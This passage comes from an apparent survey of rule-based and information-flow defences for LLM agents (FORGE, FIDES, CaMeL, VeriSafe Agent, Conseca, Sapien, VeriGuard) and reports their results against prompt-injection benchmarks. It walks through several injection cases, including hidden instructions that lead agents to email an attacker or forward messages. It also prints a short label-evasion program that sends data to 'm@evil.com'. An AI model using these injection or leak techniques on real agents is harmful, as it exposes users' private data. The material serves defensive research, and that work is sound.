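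In *Policy Compiler for Secure Agentic Systems*, Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026) introduced a system for such cases and later renamed it FORGE. It represents each message, tool call and result as a point in a graph, with an arrow from each event to any later event that it may have influenced. For instance, each message in a model's input has an arrow to the message the model then writes. Before an action, FORGE follows the arrows backward to find everything that may have influenced it. In the database example, the approval is not among the events that led to the second agent's query, so a rule can reject the query.

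The arrows show only possible influence. If a model receives ten documents and uses one, the graph still shows its answer as depending on all ten. FORGE is therefore less likely to miss an influence, but it can also block actions unnecessarily.

FORGE's rules are in Datalog, a query language that puts a conclusion to the left of the sign `:-` and the conditions for it to the right. With simplified names, this rule covers actions that send something out:

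```
Deny(action) :- SendsOut(action), Tainted(action),
                Destination(action, d), not Anchored(d).
```

The rule denies an action that sends something to a destination *d* if untrusted content may have influenced the action and *d* is not "anchored". Two further rules define a destination as anchored if it appears in the user's request or in a trusted record.

The rule allows run A if the user's contacts count as a trusted record. It blocks run B if the agent was following instructions in an untrusted document, but if the agent leaked the contacts by its own mistake, without any untrusted content, the rule lets the email through. It allows the email in run C if the user typed the organizer's address in the request. The rule handles some first emails correctly, but not those where the agent has to find the new address in an untrusted document.

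The full policy also has rules about what the user asked for. For example, the agent can delete a file only if the user asked it to delete something. If the user asks it to delete the largest file without naming it, FORGE uses the file listing to identify that file and allows the agent to delete only that one.

Palumbo and colleagues tested the policy on AgentDojo with live agents built on GPT-4o. In the main comparison, the agents also received a reminder of the user's request after each batch of tool results. FORGE reduced the success rate of attacks from 14.1% to 0.9%, but the share of harmless tasks that the agents completed fell from 83.7% to 62.5%. Under a stricter policy, which blocks important actions whenever untrusted content is anywhere in the agent's context, the agents completed only 33.2% of harmless tasks.

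FORGE blocked at least one action in 151 of the 485 harmless runs (31%), and the agents completed the task in only 36 of those 151. Some blocks may have stopped real mistakes. Kekatos and colleagues' five general obligations flagged a similar share of harmless runs (29.3%), though the two policies cover different actions, so the figures are only roughly comparable. Using the history clearly did not make false alarms rare.

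The results on customer-service tasks were much better. Palumbo and colleagues tested Claude Opus 4.5, GPT-5.2 and Gemini 3.1 Pro on τ²-bench, with FORGE rules based on the benchmark's written policies. The success rate rose from 74.7% to 81.5% on airline tasks and from 86.3% to 87.4% on retail tasks. FORGE blocked a call in 199 of 1,968 runs, and the agents still completed the task in 160 of those. FORGE most often blocked a call because the agent had skipped a check or had not obtained the customer's consent.

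One likely reason for the difference is that a customer-service agent can respond to such a block by asking the customer, which an agent in AgentDojo cannot do.

Palumbo and colleagues also had a language model translate the airline's policy into Datalog five times. They revised each translation until it agreed with a model's judgments of recorded decisions, then tested it on 15 new runs. Two of the five succeeded in all 15 runs, as the hand-written rules did, but the worst succeeded in only 10.

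Seven of the eight failures were blocked cancellations in a single task. The main error was a rule that required a reason covered by travel insurance for every cancellation, although the airline's policy requires one only if the customer is relying on the insurance. Testing the rule on the recordings could not reveal this error because they contained just three attempts to cancel, all of them violations. Even a rule that banned every cancellation would have matched all three judgments. Developers who check rules against recorded runs therefore need examples of harmless actions as well as violations.

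### Rules about what must come next

FORGE's rules can require an earlier event, but they cannot require a later one. A shop may also want its agent to send a confirmation after every refund. In Xiao and colleagues' temporal logic, this rule is

G (refund → F confirmation),

where G means "at every point in the run" and F means "now or later". As with Schneider's policy of eventually answering every customer, a monitor cannot declare a violation while the run continues. Xiao and colleagues therefore keep the obligation open. At the end of the session, ContrAgent reminds the agent of anything it still has to do, and it records a violation if the agent does not do it.

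They tested ContrAgent on SOPBench, a benchmark of customer-service tasks that come with explicit procedures. Some tasks are allowed and some forbidden. An agent built on Gemini 2.5 Flash attempted 40 tasks in each of seven domains:

| Method | Allowed tasks completed | Forbidden tasks blocked |
|---|---|---|
| No procedure | 91% | 32% |
| Procedure in the agent's instructions | 64% | 94% |
| A second model checks each call | 24% | 98% |
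| ContrAgent | 90% | 98% |

ContrAgent stopped almost all the forbidden tasks with hardly any loss on the allowed ones. When the researchers replayed safe runs from 23 models, the false-alarm rate was below 1% for 19 of them and at most 4.5% for the other four. The benchmark suits rules well because it states its procedures as explicit constraints and thresholds. Rules that use a run's history can therefore raise few false alarms if someone has already defined precisely what is allowed.

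On R-Judge, ContrAgent detected 87.0% of the unsafe records with 97.0% precision, which implies a false-alarm rate of about 3%. Kekatos and colleagues' general obligations had a detection rate of 23.6% and a false-alarm rate of 16.3%. However, ContrAgent's rules came from the benchmark's own list of risks, so its result is weak evidence of how well it would detect risks not on that list.

A precise rule can still flag behavior that does no harm. The policies in τ²-bench forbid an agent from writing to the customer and calling a tool in the same turn. Xiao and colleagues found that Claude 3.7 did this in 97% to 99% of the runs that the benchmark counted as successful. Each alarm would be correct under the policy, but blocking these calls would interrupt almost every successful run.

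### What recorded runs leave out

These rules can use only recorded history. Kekatos and colleagues measured the effect of this limit in AgentDojo's banking runs by starting with only the type of action and adding one kind of information at a time. Adding recipients and account data produced the improvement from the general payment rule to the refined one. They would have added approvals next, then times and changes to the system, but the recordings contain none of these. AgentDojo, STAC and R-Judge also don't record whether an action can be undone, which matters for any rule about deletion.

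These are the twelve fields that the researchers propose recording, with examples of rules that would need them:

| Fields | Example of a rule |
|---|---|
| `timestamp` | Consent must be less than 24 hours old |
| `actor`, `session_id` | An approval counts only for the same agent in the same session |
| `tool`, `action` | The agent may not change security settings |
| `object` | An approval to delete must name the file |
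| `recipient` | The agent may email only known contacts |
| `source`, `trust_domain` | A payee's account number must come from the user's bank records |
| `approval_id` | Every payment needs its own approval |
| `state_before`, `state_after` | A payment must not leave the account overdrawn |

The attack collections record the tool and the action, and some runs also include the object or the recipient. However, an approval field would stay empty in AgentDojo.

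Users can reply during τ-bench runs, and they send an average of 7.08 messages per run, compared with 1 in AgentDojo and 2.61 in STAC. In 52.5% of τ-bench runs, the user explicitly approves an action before the agent changes any data. This share ranges from 46.5% to 65.4% across the two domains and two models. Each approval answers an agent message with no tool call, so the user was responding to a proposal rather than giving a first instruction.

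Even there, a rule that requires approval would raise many alarms. The agent tries to change data in 88.7% of the runs, and in roughly 4 out of 10 of those, the researchers' search found no approval beforehand. The agent probably broke the policy in some of these runs. In others, the user may have agreed in words the search did not recognize, and the alarm would be false.

The benchmark's scores cannot separate violations from ordinary task steps. *τ-bench* (2024) notes that an agent can violate the policy by issuing a return without the customer's confirmation and still pass, because the score depends on the final database and the information given to the customer. Palumbo and colleagues found a similar gap in the retail part of τ²-bench. In 17 of 1,368 runs without FORGE, the agent looked up products before identifying the customer, and 13 of those 17 runs received full marks.

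Kekatos and colleagues could not measure detection on τ-bench either, because it has no labeled attacks. They recommend a new collection that combines τ-bench's conversations with AgentDojo's attack labels, so that researchers can test approval rules on runs where users actually give approvals.

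## Tracking where data flows

The email rule in the previous section checks who will receive an email but not what the email contains, so it would let an agent send Dana the whole contact list. Information-flow control can check the contents as well. Software labels each piece of data, keeps the label when it copies or combines the data, and checks it before an action uses the data. The method dates from the 1970s, but researchers have only recently applied it to agents.

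### Sources, sinks and labels

A source is anywhere an agent gets data, such as an inbox, an address book or a web page. A sink is an action that sends data out or changes something, such as emailing someone or making a payment. A confidentiality label lists who may read the data. An integrity label marks the data as trusted or untrusted. Data is usually untrusted if an outsider could have written it.

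Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, give rules for combining labels. If Ann, Bob and Carl may read one document, and Bob, Carl and Dev may read another, then only Bob and Carl may read a text that draws on both. With *R*(*x*) for the permitted readers of *x*, the rule is

*R*(text made from *x* and *y*) = *R*(*x*) ∩ *R*(*y*).

The new text is trusted only if both documents are.

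The program then checks labels at the sink. An email with body *d* may go to recipients *S* only if *S* ⊆ *R*(*d*), meaning every recipient may read the body. A payment is allowed only if the agent decided on it using trusted data alone.

### The contacts runs with one label and with several

Suppose only the user may read the contact list, while both the user and Dana may read the itinerary. The simplest design keeps one label for the model's whole context, meaning everything the model has received so far. A model can draw on any part of its context for any word it writes, and a program can't reliably tell which parts the model used. The program therefore gives the context's label to everything the model writes.

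Once step 2 adds the contact list to the context, only the user may read what the model writes. At step 3, the program blocks the leak in run B but also the itinerary in run A, because Dana is not a permitted reader. Schneider's rule against sending after reading a file has the same effect.

The other design keeps the contact list out of the context. The program stores the list in a variable and gives the model only the variable's name. The model can then write a call like this one, and the program fills in the values:

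```
send_email(to=contacts["Dana"].address, body=itinerary)
```

Each argument now has its own label. Dana is allowed to read the itinerary, so the program lets run A proceed. In run B, the body is the contact list, which the outsider is not allowed to read, so the program blocks the email.

This design requires more information about the task. Dana's address is also private data from the contact list, so someone has to decide that such an address may fill the recipient field. Someone also has to list Dana as a reader of the itinerary. A file on the user's computer would normally list only the user as a reader, so without this change the program would block run A.

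FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, avoids the second problem with an exception. An email may go out if every recipient may read it, or if the decision to send it came only from trusted data, such as the user's request. Here are the verdicts for the two contacts runs and for run C, in which the user wants a reunion organizer to have the list:

| Email | One label, no exception | Several labels, no exception | Several labels, with exception |
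|---|---|---|---|
| Run A: itinerary to Dana | Block | Allow if Dana is a listed reader | Allow |
| Run B: contact list to an outsider, after the model reads an injected instruction | Block | Block | Block |
| Run B: the same leak, by the agent's own mistake | Block | Block | Allow |
| Run C: contact list to the organizer | Block | Block | Allow |

The last two rows get the same verdict in every column because these labels don't record what the user asked for.

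### FIDES

FIDES works inside the agent's planner, the part that decides what to do next. When a tool returns data, FIDES compares each field's label with the context's label. If a field would make the context less trusted, FIDES puts it in a variable. For example, the model might receive an email's date but only variable names for its subject and body.

The planner's model can pass a variable to a tool without reading it. It can also ask a second, "quarantined" model a question about the contents. The quarantined model has no tools, so an injected instruction can corrupt its answer but can't make it act. The answer goes into another labeled variable. The planner's model can also open the original variable itself, but its context then counts as untrusted for the rest of the run.

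Suppose the user wants the agent to read three emails and create a calendar event if one of them requests a meeting. The planner's model can send the quarantined model a yes-or-no question and read only the answer. An attacker can control just one bit through that answer, whereas a free-text answer could contain a new instruction. The answer's label also records its type, so a policy can accept yes-or-no answers for this reason.

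Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo without these restricted answers. With GPT-4o and no defense, 152 attacks succeeded. Hiding untrusted data in variables reduced this to 21, and adding the policy checks reduced it to 0. (AgentDojo's own scoring counted 3 successes with the checks on, but the researchers judged that none of them was a real injection.)

The next table shows the percentage of harmless tasks each agent completed. The last column is the average of the paper's figures, weighted by the number of tasks in each domain.

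| Model and defense | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack | All 97 tasks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, none | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 | 81.9 |
| GPT-4o, one label on the context | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 | 40.8 |
| GPT-4o, FIDES | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 | 51.7 |
| o1, none | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 | 80.6 |
| o1, one label on the context | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 | 45.1 |
| o1, FIDES | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 | 61.6 |

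With a single label on the context, the agents completed about half as many tasks, and FIDES recovered some of the lost ones. Travel tasks were the exception. A single label does little harm there because many tools may run in an untrusted context as long as nothing private leaks, and GPT-4o often misused FIDES's variables. The reasoning model o1 handled the variables better.

A better model would not recover all the lost tasks. The right next action depends on what the agent reads in 44% of the banking tasks and 43% of the Slack tasks, but in only 5% of the workspace tasks and 10% of the travel tasks. For example, the user may ask the agent to follow the instructions in a file. Opening the file makes the context untrusted, so FIDES blocks the payment requested in the file, as its designers intended.

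The security result also depends on unusually good labels. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if at least one of AgentDojo's attacks used it. A company doesn't know which fields attackers will use, so it would have to either mark more fields, and have its agent complete fewer tasks, or risk leaving some of the attacked fields unmarked.

### CaMeL

CaMeL, which Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, also has a planner and a quarantined model, but the planner finishes its work before any data arrives. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, describe how it works. The planner's model receives only the user's request and descriptions of the tools, and it writes a Python program for the whole task. Simplified, the program for the itinerary might be:

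```
itinerary = find_file("itinerary")
contacts = list_contacts()
address = contacts["Dana"].address
send_email(to=address, body=itinerary)
```

CaMeL runs this program in its own interpreter, which records which earlier values each value came from. Before each tool call, it checks the arguments and their history against the policies. The planner has already written the program, so an instruction hidden in the itinerary can't add a line to it. But the data can still affect which branch of the program runs. If the plan is to book a hotel only when its reviews are good, whoever writes the reviews can influence the booking.

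Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each, with and without its policy checks. Some of the attacked runs did not finish, so the attack totals differ:

| | GPT-5.2 | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless tasks completed, no policies | 32 of 48 | 34 of 48 |
| Harmless tasks completed, with policies | 18 of 48 | 18 of 48 |
| Successful attacks, no policies | 1 of 240 | 4 of 382 |
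| Successful attacks, with policies | 0 of 231 | 0 of 357 |

The fixed plan provided nearly all of the protection. In 97 of the 144 task-attack pairs, the attack needs a tool call or file that no sensible plan for the task would include. The policies stopped the few attacks that still succeeded, but with them on, the agents completed only a little over half as many tasks. The exact size of this loss is uncertain because there were only 16 tasks. Garby and colleagues report a similar result for another system, TypeGuard, which completed 15 of 21 Slack tasks with its policies off and 8 with them on. CaMeL completed 7 under the same conditions.

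Two of the five successful attacks exploited the same task, in which the user asks the agent to precisely follow the instructions in a file. The planner wrote a loop that turned each instruction into a tool call. The program was fixed in advance, but whoever wrote the file could make it do almost anything.

Peters-Gill and colleagues tested newer models on a version of AgentDojo that divides each task among several agents, running 949 attacks per model. With its policies turned off, CaMeL reduced the attacks' success rate from 36.1% to 0.5% for GPT-4.1, from 24.6% to 0.4% for Gemini 2.5 Pro, from 2.1% to 0% for Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite and from 1.5% to 0% for Claude Fable 5. No attack succeeded against GPT-5.5, even without CaMeL.

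Every attack that got past CaMeL succeeded because a label was lost when one agent passed data to another. In the researchers' demonstration, the user asks for a summary of job applicants to be sent to Julie on Slack. One agent reads the applicant database, where an attacker has hidden an instruction. A coordinating agent then pastes the summary into its request to a third agent, which sends messages. The third agent treats the whole request as trusted, so its planner adds a step that emails the attacker. The researchers fixed this by sending instructions and data through separate channels, after which no attacks succeeded.

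On AssetOpsBench, a benchmark of professional tasks for teams of agents, CaMeL lowered the task completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across the five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Most failures happened because an agent discovered during the run that it needed a tool the plan didn't include. CaMeL is also much slower than lightweight defenses, partly because it writes longer programs, according to *ToolFence* (2026).

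### Who may remove a label

Labels, like the arrows in FORGE's graph, follow every possible influence, so they often spread to data that their source hardly affected. This is called over-tainting. Palumbo and colleagues measured it by applying FIDES's policy to an ordinary GPT-4o agent without hidden variables. The policy blocked at least one action in 287 of 485 harmless runs, and the agent completed the task in only 10 of those 287.

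To allow such tasks, someone has to remove labels. Removing a confidentiality label is called declassification, and removing an "untrusted" label is called endorsement. A developer can write some exceptions in advance, like the one for yes-or-no answers, but others depend on the task. For example, a file from outside should not normally control a payment, but the user may have asked the agent to make the payment described in the file.

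Garby and colleagues leave this decision to the planner's model. Their agent, Randori, also writes its plan as a program, and the model can include an explicit `endorse` step for data that the task needs. The model adds any such step before it reads outside data, so an attacker can't manipulate it into adding one. The researchers also proved that endorsing untrusted data this way can't cause private data to leak.

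With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 36 of 48 banking runs, while CaMeL with policies completed 18. Without endorsement, Randori completed 30 runs instead of 36 with Qwen3.7-plus, and 26 instead of 31 with MiMo-v2.5. Across the three models, 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user asked the agent to follow payment instructions in a text file, and the attacker had replaced the text. Without endorsement, the program would block this attack, but it would also block the payment when the file is genuine.

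*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) leaves the decision to the user instead. Its agent, Prudentia, extends FIDES by telling the planner's model about the labels and policies, so it can take them into account when planning. Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse data. If an email contains a to-do list with ten items, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten actions.

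Prudentia does not offer declassification. Kolluri and colleagues considered it but decided that whether private data may leave is "often highly dependent on the situation", so the agent asks about each action separately. For example, if the user declassified the contact list in run C so that it could go to the reunion organizer, the agent could then send it to anyone. A narrower permission would have to name the organizer, which would make it a rule about this particular task.

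### What labels miss

Labels restrict where data may go, but they don't show whether it is true or harmful. Suppose a user asks for a summary of recent emails to be sent to a manager, and one of the emails contains an instruction to leave the summary empty. The quarantined model may follow that instruction, and FIDES will send the empty summary because the user chose the action and the recipient. Costa and colleagues note that a stricter policy could also require the contents to be trusted, but that would block accurate summaries of untrusted emails too.

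This problem can be more expensive when an agent makes payments. In the AgentDojo tests, FIDES's payment rule checked whether the decision to pay was trusted, but ignored the labels on the account number and amount. This lets an agent pay a genuine bill without opening it in the planner's context. But if someone has replaced the account number in the bill with their own, the rule also lets the agent pay them.

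Some attacks don't need a tool call. When Palumbo and colleagues ran FIDES's policy together with repeated reminders of the user's request, 12 of 4,745 attacks still had an effect. All 12 came from an attack that tries to make the agent recommend a particular hotel in its reply. The policy checks only tool calls, so it never checked the reply. An application could at least warn the user that the recommendation draws on untrusted text.

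Private data can also leak through the agent's choices. FIDES stops private data from flowing directly to people who aren't allowed to read it, but someone who sees which tools the agent calls may still learn something about that data. Noninterference would rule this out, but it is not a property of a single run, and Costa and colleagues consider it too restrictive to enforce.

CaMeL does track some of these choices. It blocks an email that the program sends only if the user's bank balance is above a threshold. But Garby and colleagues found that an old trick gets around the check. This program uses it:

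```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and gets a private label. The program then skips the fourth line, so `rich` stays true and keeps its public label. The email goes out and reveals that the balance is high. An attacker would still have to get these lines into the plan, which is difficult when the planner doesn't read outside data. The example mainly shows that tracking labels correctly is harder than it looks. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) adds that features of Python such as dynamic typing make strong guarantees difficult.

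A tracker that monitors only tool calls can also lose track of data when an agent runs a script, because the script can read a file and send it without making another tool call. For this reason, *ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) attaches labels in the operating system.

### Whether the protection is worth the lost tasks

The main argument for labels is that the check doesn't depend on a model recognizing an attack. An attacker can keep rewording an instruction until a model follows it, but rewording doesn't change the label on the email that contains the instruction. This protection covers only the flows the policy forbids, and it holds only if the labels are correct.

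The measured benefit is small for the newest models. GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 AgentDojo attacks without any labels, and it completed fewer tasks with CaMeL. However, these attacks are fixed texts from 2024. Peters-Gill and colleagues point to a large test in which attackers adapted to each model, and some attacks succeeded against every leading model. Resisting every AgentDojo attack is therefore weak evidence that a model needs no other protection.

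Kolluri and colleagues argue that the usual comparison also overstates the cost of labels. It compares a protected agent with one that may pay and send mail without asking anyone, whereas many real products ask the user to approve every important action. They counted the AgentDojo tasks that agents built on o3-mini could finish with no approvals:

| Agent | Tasks completed without approval |
|---|---|
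| Must ask before every important action | 24.3% |
| One label on the context | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | 59.1% |

With labels, an agent can do more by itself than one that must always ask for approval. The researchers assume that an action needs no approval if it passes the policy check. This is reasonable for prompt injection but not for the agent's own mistakes. A company that requires approval because its agent sometimes picks the wrong person named Dana would still need to require it.

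Labels interfere less with a task when the user's request already determines the steps, as in most of AgentDojo's email and calendar tasks. They interfere much more in banking and Slack tasks, where the agent often has to read something before it can choose its next step.

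## Writing the rules from the user's instruction

Labels on data can't distinguish run C, in which the user wants a reunion organizer to have the contact list, from an accidental leak of the same list, because the two differ only in what the user requested. Lee and colleagues' system, VeriSafe Agent, therefore has a language model turn each request into its own set of rules before the agent starts. Progent also writes rules for each task, but it checks tool calls, which name their recipient or amount. VeriSafe Agent works on phone apps, where the agent only taps, swipes and types.

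### Rules for a restaurant booking

VeriSafe Agent requires each app's developer to declare "states" that describe the facts that matter in the app. A restaurant app might have a state called `RestaurantInfo`, with a text variable called `name`. The developer also attaches a trigger to each important button. When the agent presses the button, the trigger works out how the states would change and reports this before the app's own code runs. The verifier can then check the effect of a tap in advance, although the tap itself is only a pair of coordinates.

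In Lee and colleagues' main example, the user wants a table at restaurant R before 7 pm, and wants the agent to do nothing if no table is available. A model, GPT-4o in their tests, receives this instruction and the list of states, and writes three rules:

```
R1: RestaurantInfo(name = "R")
    ∧ ReserveInfo(date = Today, time < 19:00, available = True)
    → Reserve

R2: Reserve ∧ ReserveResult(success = True) → Done

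R3: RestaurantInfo(name = "R")
    ∧ ReserveInfo(date = Today, time < 19:00, available ≠ True)
    → Done
```

Each rule is a Horn clause, a formula with a single conclusion and a list of conditions joined by "and". R1 lets the agent reserve only if the restaurant is R and the chosen time is today, before 7 pm and free. Under R2, the task is done once the reservation has succeeded. Under R3, it is also done if the chosen time is not free.

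Before the agent starts, VeriSafe Agent checks these rules in two ways. A program looks for errors in syntax and type, such as the condition `name ≥ 100`, which compares a text variable with a number. Then one model translates the rules back into English, and another compares the translation with the user's instruction. If either check finds a problem, the model that wrote the rules must revise them.

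From then on, a program checks the conditions after each reported change. If the agent picks restaurant S, `name = "R"` becomes false, and the program can show the agent which condition failed.

### The contacts runs again

The developer of an email app could declare a state called `Draft`, with variables for the recipient and the attachment. For the instruction "send the itinerary to Dana", the model might then write:

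```
Draft(recipient = "Dana", attachment = "itinerary") → Send
Send ∧ SendResult(success = True) → Done
```

Neither rule mentions the contacts, so the agent can open them at step 2 without triggering an alarm. At step 3, run A satisfies the first rule, and run B violates it because the recipient and the attachment are both wrong. The first rule also stops the agent from sending Dana the whole contact list, which a rule about recipients alone would allow. In run C, the model would start from a different instruction and write a rule that names the organizer and the contact list, so the email could go out.

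However, the rules cover only what the instruction mentions. Suppose the agent posts the contact list on a social network and then emails Dana the itinerary. The email satisfies both rules, and neither covers posts. Progent would block the post because it blocks every call that no rule allows. VeriSafe Agent's rules state what must be true before the agent reaches a goal, and they do not ban other actions.

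### Three apples, one at a time

Many harmless tasks go through states that break the rule. If a user asks for three apples and the agent adds them one at a time, the condition "quantity = 3" is false after the first and second apples. A verifier that blocked the agent whenever a condition was false would never let it reach three.

Lee and colleagues therefore treat ordinary and critical actions differently. When an ordinary action makes a condition false, the verifier holds it back and warns the agent, but lets it through if the agent proposes it again. Before a critical action, such as placing the order, every condition in the relevant rule must be true, or the verifier blocks the action however often the agent proposes it. This fits Schneider's theory, in which a monitor has to wait for a step that shows the run is unacceptable.

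The agent itself marks which actions are critical. Lee and colleagues changed its prompt so that it flags any action meant to achieve a goal in the rules, such as `Reserve`. If the agent in run B fails to flag the tap on "Send", the verifier only gives a warning, and the agent can leak the contacts by tapping again. An attacker who controls the agent could make it leave out the flag. Lee and colleagues designed the system for agents that make mistakes and did not test it against attackers. One possible fix is to let the developer, who already attaches a trigger to the "Send" button, mark that button as critical.

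### Accuracy on 300 instructions

Lee and colleagues tested VeriSafe Agent on 300 instructions in 18 apps. The recorded actions matched the instruction in half of the cases. Most tasks were simple, with an average of 5.67 steps, but 50 cases came from harder tasks, which averaged 19.16 steps and went up to 40. In one of these, the agent has to find a well-reviewed attraction near Florence's cathedral and then show a wheelchair-accessible walking route to it.

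The researchers compared two versions of their system with models that review each action before or after the agent takes it. The counts in this table follow from the paper's precision and recall figures:

| Verifier | False alarms, simple tasks | Missed errors, simple tasks | False alarms, harder tasks | Missed errors, harder tasks | Accuracy, all 300 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Model reviews before the action | 36 of 125 | 13 of 125 | 15 of 25 | 1 of 25 | 78.3% |
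| Model reviews after the action | 7 of 125 | 6 of 125 | 8 of 25 | 4 of 25 | 91.7% |
| VeriSafe Agent, no memory | 7 of 125 | 4 of 125 | 5 of 25 | 1 of 25 | 94.3% |
| VeriSafe Agent, with memory | 2 of 125 | 0 of 125 | 2 of 25 | 1 of 25 | 98.3% |

In the best case, the system had a false-alarm rate of 2.7% and missed 0.7% of the errors. These results came from a version that stores conditions that worked before, and the test assumed that suitable ones were already stored for each instruction. The version without this memory is a better guide to how the system would handle a new request. It raised false alarms in 8% of the correct cases, and in 20% of the harder ones.

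The rules also helped the agent finish its work, because the verifier's feedback listed the conditions still to be met. The agent completed 10 of the 25 harder tasks without feedback, 19 with VeriSafe Agent, and 23 when the system also had its memory. Feedback from the reviewing models did not help the agent complete any task it had failed.

VeriSafe Agent is also cheaper than a reviewing model on long tasks. It uses models mainly at the start, so its cost hardly grows with the number of steps. A reviewing model has to run for every action, which roughly doubles the cost of running the agent.

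These results may look better than they would in ordinary use because the researchers made the incorrect cases by altering the instructions. For example, they changed a request for top-selling books to one for newly released books and kept the old recording. The error was therefore always in a detail the user had mentioned, which is the kind of detail the rules capture.

The researchers also had no access to the apps' source code, so they labeled the states and triggers on the screens by hand. The test does not show how well app developers would label them. For some text comparisons, the program uses a model to convert each text into an embedding, a list of numbers that represents its meaning, and counts two texts as equal if their similarity reaches 0.7. This lets "Jan 01" match "January 1st", but a person's name often needs an exact match, and the paper gives no error rate for these comparisons.

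The size of the advantage over reviewing models is also uncertain. In *VeriSafe Agent*, the slides for a conference talk, Lee, Lee and colleagues (2025) give the same F1 scores for their own system as the paper does, but much lower ones for the reviewing models. On the harder tasks, the better of these models scores 59.6 in the slides and 77.8 in the paper.

### Conseca's policy for each request

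Conseca, a Google prototype described in *Contextual Agent Security* (Tsai and Bagdasarian, 2025), applies the same idea to an agent that runs commands on a Linux computer. A model writes a policy from the user's request and "trusted context", meaning information that an attacker probably can't change. In the prototype, this includes the user's email addresses, the names of files and folders, and the date, but not the contents of emails, so an instruction hidden in an email cannot influence the policy.

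For each command, the policy specifies whether the agent may use it, what the arguments must look like, and why. For example, a user called Alice asks the agent to read unread work emails and answer the urgent ones. The model's policy forbids deleting emails. It allows sending them only if Alice is the sender, the recipient has a work address and the subject contains "urgent". An ordinary program then compares each command with these patterns.

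This policy contains a translation error. The user meant emails that need a quick answer, but the rule checks for a particular word in the reply's subject line, so it would block "Re: server down". The pattern is case-sensitive, so it would also block "Re: URGENT: server down".

Tsai and Bagdasarian tested Conseca on 20 tasks, with five attempts at each. The agent completed an average of 14.0 tasks without a policy and 12.0 with Conseca. It did about as well under a fixed policy that allowed everything except deletion, completing 12.2, but completed none under one that banned all changes.

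The researchers also planted an email that told the reader to forward messages about security problems to another employee. The unrestricted agent forwarded them even when the user had only asked it to sort emails. Conseca blocked the forwarding in every task except the one where the user had asked the agent to carry out the tasks in urgent emails. This test covered one attack on a small set of invented tasks, so it mainly illustrates that the same action can be allowed or blocked depending on the user's request.

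Conseca checks each action separately. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) points out that an attacker who controls the agent could therefore combine several permitted actions into a harmful one. Tsai and Bagdasarian also recognized that policies that cover whole runs would be useful, and Tsai later worked on a system that has such policies.

### Sapien adds the history of the run

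*Sapien* (Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) lets the model write rules that depend on what the agent has already done and read. This helps because requests often refer to facts the agent hasn't found yet. For example, "Refund the person who sent me money last week" doesn't specify the person or the amount. A Sapien policy can require the agent to list the transactions first, then allow a payment only if last week's entries show the recipient as a sender and include the amount.

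In simplified form, a policy for the itinerary could be:

```
find_file@doc . list_contacts@people .
  send_email(to=PREDICATE(is_dana), body=PREDICATE(is_itinerary))
```

The dots mean "then", and the `@` sign saves a result under a name. Along with the policy, the model writes two small Python functions, `is_dana` and `is_itinerary`. `is_dana` checks that the recipient is the address listed for Dana in `people`, and `is_itinerary` compares the email with the file in `doc`. The user only has to say "Dana", and the program finds the address in the contacts.

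Tiffany and colleagues tested this on AgentDojo with four recent models, including Claude Opus 5 and Gemini 3.8 Flash. With Sapien, each agent completed one to five fewer of the 97 harmless tasks than without it. Sapien blocked at least one call in 20 of 388 harmless runs, or about 5%, and the agent failed the task in 11 of those 20. FORGE, whose rules were the same for every task, blocked calls in 31% of its harmless AgentDojo runs. The agents in the FORGE study used an older model, so the rules may not account for the whole difference.

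To measure security, the researchers assumed that an attacker had taken over the agent and could make it propose any call. They counted an attack as stopped only if no permitted sequence of calls would achieve the attacker's goal. This is a harder test than planting an instruction and seeing whether the model follows it.

| | AgentDojo, 949 attacks | Toolathlon, 212 attacks |
|---|---|---|
| List of allowed tools for each task | 82.7% to 86.8% stopped | 32.4% stopped |
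| Sapien | 93.2% to 95.2% stopped | 64.6% stopped |

(The ranges cover the four models. The full Toolathlon test used only Gemini 3.8 Flash.)

Toolathlon is a benchmark of longer tasks, and the researchers chose attacks on it that use the tools the task itself needs, so a list of tools does little to stop them. Tiffany and colleagues modeled the list on Conseca, but Conseca can also restrict arguments, so the table probably understates what Conseca would stop. Most of the attacks that got past Sapien changed what the agent wrote, such as the text of a report, which the rules could not reliably check.

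Writing such policies took an average of 43 to 100 seconds per task on AgentDojo, depending on the model, and made up about two-thirds of the total running time. Checking a call against the finished policy usually took less than a millisecond.

### VeriGuard proves its policy code correct

*VeriGuard* (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025) adds a mathematical proof. It starts from a safety request, such as a ban on emails to addresses outside the company. Before the agent is used, a model writes a Python function that allows or denies an action, and a separate list of constraints on that function. VeriGuard asks the user about anything ambiguous or, if no user is available, chooses the most plausible reading itself. It then tests the function and passes it to Nagini, a program that proves statements about Python code.

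Nagini tries to prove that if the conditions *C*pre hold before the function *p* runs, the conditions *C*post will hold afterward. This claim is called a Hoare triple and is written {*C*pre} *p* {*C*post}. If the proof fails, the model revises its code.

The proof covers only the function. While the agent works, another model reads the agent's inputs and outputs and extracts the values the function needs, such as a list of recipients. If this model overlooks an outside address, the function will correctly approve the incomplete list. The live check is therefore not fully deterministic, even though the function is.

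In tests on the benchmark ASB, no attack succeeded against VeriGuard. But no attack succeeded against a simpler defense either, in which a model judged directly whether the agent was following the policy. The difference was in how many of their own tasks the agents completed:

| Agent's model | No attack | Attack, no defense | Attack, model as judge | Attack, VeriGuard |
|---|---|---|---|---|
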